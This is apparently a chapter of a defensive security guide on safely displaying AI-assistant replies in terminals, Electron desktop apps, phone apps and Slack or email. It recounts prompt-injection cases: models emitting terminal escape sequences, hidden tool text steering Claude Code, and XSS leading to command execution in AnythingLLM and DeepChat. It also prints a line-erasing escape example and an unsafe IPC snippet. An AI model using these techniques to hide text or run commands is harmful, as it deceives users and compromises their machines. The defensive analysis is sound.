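Many people will ignore a displayed address, and many who read it will misunderstand it. Reynolds and colleagues gave some participants the help that browsers provide, such as highlighting the host and removing the user part. Those participants identified 61.1% of all the addresses, slightly more than the 56.1% identified by the others.

Users of AI assistants may pay even less attention. Ouyang and Narechania asked 12 students to judge the accuracy of answers from nine assistants and recorded how they used the references. ChatGPT's references got the most attention, but participants hovered over only about 22% of them and clicked about 12%. They were still mostly satisfied with the answers. The study is small, and mouse movements don't show when someone looks at a reference without pointing at it, but the results suggest that few users will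 see a label that appears only on hover.

Hostile links can still be dangerous despite the low click rates for those references, which participants had little reason to open. A false security notice, by contrast, tells the user to act at once. In the experiment by Petelka and colleagues, 57% to 63% of participants clicked call-to-action links in harmless emails, compared with 48.5% for harmless links overall.

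Explaining an address can help people much more than highlighting its domain. Althobaiti, Meng and Vaniea (2021), in *I Don't Need an Expert! Making URL Phishing Features Human Comprehensible*, gave 153 people different amounts of explanation about an address. Those with a full report judged its safety correctly 93% of the time, compared with 83% for those with a summary and 65% for those with only a highlighted domain. Few people will read a report for every link, but an application could offer a short summary for links that its own checks flag as suspicious.

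A visible domain also helps people other than the user about to click. A colleague looking at a shared conversation may notice that the domain is wrong, and a user who reports a strange reply can tell the security team which domain to look for in its logs. Displaying the domain takes little extra work, since the application has to parse the address anyway, so it is worth doing to guard against deceptive sites.

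Showing the address works much less well against leaks, because users can't be expected to know whether `?d=4731` is an article number or their own door code. The application can instead check the exact address, as it would for an image, then open known links normally and show the confirmation page only for the rest. Users will then see that page rarely enough to take it seriously.

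## Terminals, desktop programs and phone apps

Content security policies, sandboxed frames and `setHTML()` are browser features, but many people read model output in terminals, desktop programs, Slack channels or phone apps. Some of these programs contain a browser engine with looser rules, and others have no browser engine.

### Control sequences in a terminal

A terminal is a text window where users type commands and read the results. It displays most characters as they are but treats a few as instructions. The most important is the escape character (1b in hexadecimal), which begins a control sequence. David Leadbeater, writing on dgl.cx, traces these sequences to an old ANSI standard for displays and printers. Programs use them to colour text and move the cursor. The terminal carries them out regardless of who wrote them, so a program that prints a stranger's text unchanged lets the stranger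 control the screen.

Suppose the mailbox assistant has a command-line version. Here `\x1b` stands for the escape character:

```
in the reply     Sender not verified.\x1b[2K\x1b[1GSender verified.
on the screen    Sender verified.
```

The first sequence erases the line and the second moves the cursor back to its start. The user sees only the second sentence, but a model that rereads the conversation receives both.

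| What a sequence can do | Result |
|---|---|
| Give text the same colour as the background | The user can't see text that the model can read |
| Move the cursor or clear the screen | Later text replaces earlier text |
| Create a link with its own wording | The link can hide its destination and carry private data |
| Write to the clipboard | The user may paste a command they never copied |
| Make the macOS Terminal look up a host name | The name can carry private data out without a click |

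In November 2024, Leon Derczynski described how language models can write the escape character. Rehberger built on this the following month in Embrace The Red's *Terminal DiLLMa*. He wrote a program that sent a file or web page to GPT-4o and printed the answer in the terminal. When he asked it to summarise a page with planted instructions, the answer changed the text colour, moved the cursor, cleared the screen and beeped. Some demonstrations took several tries. The attack was more reliable when the planted text already contained control characters for the model to copy.

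Rehberger also produced a link containing data from the prompt. The terminal in the code editor VS Code made it clickable, but asked for confirmation before opening it. Apple's terminal didn't support such links, but it did look up the host name. Most terminals he tested removed the final line break from text written to the clipboard so that a pasted command would not run immediately, but at least one kept the line break.

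*The Attack and Defense Landscape of Agentic AI* (2026) describes an earlier case, a 2023 flaw in AutoGPT, an early agent that printed the web pages it fetched straight to the terminal. Control sequences in a page could hide the commands that AutoGPT ran, or trick the user into approving one, without the model following any instructions. A program therefore has to clean all outside text before printing it, including web pages, file names and error messages.

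### Command-line agents and their approval prompts

Coding agents often ask the user before running a command, but this protects the user only if the screen shows what the agent is about to do. Trail of Bits' *Deceiving users with ANSI terminal codes in MCP* (2025) found that Claude Code version 0.2.76 did not filter control sequences from the descriptions and results of outside tools. In one test, a tool returned an ordinary description of the user's computers that included a sentence in white text on the terminal's default background, which said that Python downloads had to come from a particular server. Claude then recommended that server to the user.

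The white text would show up on a dark background, but an attacker can instead move the cursor and write over the text to hide it. In another example from Trail of Bits, a false report of a clean security scan overwrote an instruction to send out the user's environment variables, which often contain secret keys.

Later advisories describe similar flaws in other tools:

- **OpenClaw**, an open-source agent, copied control sequences from tool titles into its approval prompts. OSV's *GHSA-4hmj-39m8-jwc7* (2026) rates the flaw medium. The fix cleans the titles where they enter the program and makes an existing filter cover more kinds of sequence. The entry gives the first safe version as 2026.3.25 in one place and 2026.3.28 in another, so the later one is the safer choice.
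- **GitHub's command-line tool** printed pull requests, releases and agent tasks without cleaning them. An earlier fix had covered only one command, for viewing logs. According to OSV's *CVE-2026-64654* (2026), the effects ranged from a changed window title to running commands in some terminals. Version 2.97.0 fixes it.
- **Claude HUD**, a plugin for Claude Code, built terminal links from folder names and branch addresses. VulnCheck's *claude hud terminal injection via osc 8 hyperlinks* explains that a crafted name could end the link early and add sequences of its own, which could forge a prompt or write to the clipboard.

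### Making control characters visible

Trail of Bits suggests replacing every escape character with a placeholder. This disables the sequences in the table, but a reply can still rewrite text with a backspace, which Rehberger tested. MITRE's *CWE-150*, updated in April 2026 with advice on language models, recommends allowing only printable characters and selected whitespace. It mentions the carriage return as whitespace a developer might allow, but a carriage return by itself moves the cursor to the start of the line, where the next words can overwrite the previous ones.

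This function keeps tabs and line breaks and makes all other control characters visible:

```js
function forTerminal(text) {
  return text
    .replace(/\r\n/g, "\n")
    .replace(/[\x00-\x08\x0b-\x1f\x7f-\x9f]/g,
      (c) => "\\x" + c.charCodeAt(0).toString(16).padStart(2, "0"));
}
```

The last range includes single characters that some terminals accept in place of a longer sequence. The function checks each character separately, so it also works on streamed replies, where a sequence may be split across two fragments.

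Harmless replies lose any colours the model added. The program can restore colour by parsing the markdown, encoding the text in each node, and then adding its own sequences for headings and code.

Deleting control characters gives tidier output, but it is risky in an approval prompt. MITRE lists an application that removed control sequences from a file name in its permission dialog but kept them in the name it used, so the user could approve access to the wrong file. Showing the sequences in a visible encoding would have exposed the difference.

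Ordinary spaces can hide text too. Tracebit found that Google's Gemini CLI ran a whole command without displaying the part that followed a long run of whitespace. An approval prompt should replace such a run with a visible note of its length and show everything after it.

MITRE also suggests removing escape codes from a model's vocabulary during training, but rates its effectiveness as limited because the model may still build a code from several tokens.

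### Desktop programs built from web pages

Many desktop assistants, including ChatGPT Classic, use Electron, which contains a browser engine and Node.js, a system for running JavaScript outside a browser. *Buzz to Boom* (Yu, Liu and colleagues, 2026) explains that Electron's main process can read files and run commands, while renderer processes display the pages. A small program called a preload script gives each page selected functions for sending requests to the main process.

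With safe settings, code injected into the page can reach the computer only through the functions that the preload script exposes. AnythingLLM Desktop had unsafe settings, so the XSS flaw in its streamed replies gave attackers access to much more than the conversation. According to Wiz's *CVE-2026-32626*, it had `nodeIntegration` on, which gives page code direct access to Node.js, and `contextIsolation` off, which removes the barrier between the page and the preload script. A document with planted instructions could therefore cause commands to run on the user's computer after the user asked an ordinary question. MITRE's *AnythingLLM has a Streaming Phase XSS to RCE via LLM Response Injection* (2026) scores the severity at 9.7 out of 10.

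Version 1.11.2 fixes the flaw by running DOMPurify on the streamed reply. Wiz lists correcting the two settings as additional hardening, which suggests that the fix did not change them. INCIBE's *CVE-2024-3166* (2024) had already attributed an earlier flaw to the same settings, in which a web page added to a workspace could run commands. If AnythingLLM keeps these settings, another XSS flaw could be just as serious.

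In DeepChat, another desktop assistant, code injected through Mermaid diagrams could send messages that made the main process run commands on the computer. OSV's *CVE-2025-58768* (2025) describes the flaw, rated 9.6, in which DeepChat assigned diagram content to `innerHTML`. An earlier fix had missed this route, which version 0.3.5 closed. A second Mermaid flaw followed in December 2025. MITRE's *CVE-2025-67744* attributes it to unsafe diagram settings combined with the same kind of exposed messaging, and lists version 0.5.3 as fixed.

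The preload script should offer the page a few specific tasks instead of a general way to send messages:

```js
// dangerous: the page can send any message to the main process
contextBridge.exposeInMainWorld("ipc", {
  send: (channel, data) => ipcRenderer.send(channel, data),
});

// better: the page can ask for one thing
contextBridge.exposeInMainWorld("chat", {
  openLink: (address) => ipcRenderer.invoke("open-link", address),
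});
```

Even the second version is unsafe if the main process opens every address it receives. SecureLayer7's *DeepChat openExternal RCE via XSS in Electron* reports that DeepChat passed any address to Electron's `openExternal` function, which asks the operating system to open the address with whatever program handles that type.

Electron's security guide lists settings and checks that limit the damage from injected code. These matter most for a chat program:

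| Setting or check | What it limits | Electron's default |
|---|---|---|
| `nodeIntegration: false` | Direct access to Node.js | Safe since version 5 |
| `contextIsolation: true` | Tampering with the preload script | Safe since version 12 |
| `sandbox: true` | What the renderer can do on the computer | Safe in current versions |
| Content security policy | Scripts and automatic requests | None |
| Navigation and new-window handlers | Opening an attacker's page inside the program | The developer must write them |
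| Address check before `openExternal` | Starting other programs | The developer must write it |
| Sender check on each message | Requests from embedded frames | The developer must write it |
| Permission handler | Features such as notifications | Electron approves every request |

A team can easily lose its content security policy when it turns its website into a desktop program. If the program loads the page from disk through a `file://` address, no server sends the policy header, so the developer has to put the policy in a `meta` element. The new-window handler should refuse to open windows by default and show the user any address before passing it to the normal browser. ChatGPT's desktop program leaked messages through a window that opened without a click.

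These settings don't make the main process safe. Yu and colleagues tested 589 Electron programs with an automated tool and found 23 new flaws, 22 of which let an attacker run commands. Their attacks began with a link that opens a desktop program, such as a `paperlib:` link for the reference manager Paperlib. After the victim clicked the link and confirmed it in the browser, Paperlib passed the attacker's data between three processes and ran a command. These attacks did not involve AI replies, but a chat application that allows custom schemes in replies could deliver such a link.

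Tauri, an alternative to Electron, lets developers grant permissions to each window separately, so a window that displays replies can be denied file access. Tauri's *Capabilities* warns that every window can use all the commands the developer has written by default, and that the permission system can't protect against insecure code in a permitted command.

### Native components in phone apps and code editors

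Many phone apps and some code editors display markdown without making a web page. They turn each node of the syntax tree into a native component, such as the operating system's text box or image view. An event handler in the reply then has no page to run in, which removes most of the XSS risk.

Images are just as dangerous in apps. An image component typically downloads its picture as soon as it appears, using the app's own network code. The website's content security policy does not apply to that request, so the app needs its own address check. ChatGPT's iPhone app at first lacked this check in 2023. The check belongs in the one function that downloads all images, so that a new feature can't bypass it. Network libraries usually follow redirects automatically, so the function must also check each new address or refuse redirects.

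A check on the server protects even people who haven't updated the app. To avoid differences between the server's parser and the app's, the server can send a checked syntax tree instead of markdown. In that tree, it can replace each permitted image with an identifier that only the application's own image server can resolve.

Native text boxes can turn bare web addresses and phone numbers into links after the markdown filter has finished, so developers should disable this feature for replies. The app should also check a tapped link's scheme against its allowlist before passing the link to the operating system, which may open another app.

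Some apps display replies in a web view, a browser component inside the app. A content security policy works there if the page includes one, but any native functions the app exposes to the page need the same limits as Electron's preload functions.

### Messages, emails and link previews

An assistant that replies in a chat program cannot control how that program displays the message. Link previews, which are on by default according to Slack's *Unfurling links in messages*, can leak a secret contained in a link's URL, such as a door code, even if nobody clicks the link. Slack's servers fetch the link, so no setting in the user's browser can stop the request.

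INCIBE's *CVE-2025-34072* (2025) records this flaw in Anthropic's discontinued Slack connector for agents, with a severity of 9.3. In February 2026, PromptArmor demonstrated the same leak in several combinations of agents and chat programs, including Slack, Discord, and Microsoft Teams with Copilot Studio, according to TechNadu's *AI Agents Leak Data via Messaging App Link Previews*. PromptArmor's *Data Exfil from Agents in Messaging Apps* found that OpenClaw was exposed by default when used through Telegram. Setting `linkPreview` to `false` in OpenClaw's Telegram configuration stops the previews.

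For Slack, the program that posts the reply has to add two fields to every message, as Embrace The Red's *The dangers of AI agents unfurling hyperlinks and what to do about it* shows:

```json
{
  "text": "Your parcel arrives on Tuesday.",
  "unfurl_links": false,
  "unfurl_media": false
}
```

Users lose the previews of harmless links, but every link still works, so a click can leak data. The program should therefore check addresses before it posts the message.

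The two fields don't help when a user copies a reply and posts it to Slack, because Slack treats it as the user's own message. A "Copy" button can make this worse if it copies the model's original markdown. That text includes the full address of any image the application refused to load, and another program may load the image when the user pastes the text. The button should copy from the filtered syntax tree, leaving out blocked addresses.

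The recipient's mail program decides whether to load images in an email, and some security products open links in incoming mail to check them. Sending a reply as plain text prevents images from loading, but the mail program may still turn a web address into a link, and a scanner may still open it. Before sending an email, an assistant should therefore remove any web address that fails its checks.
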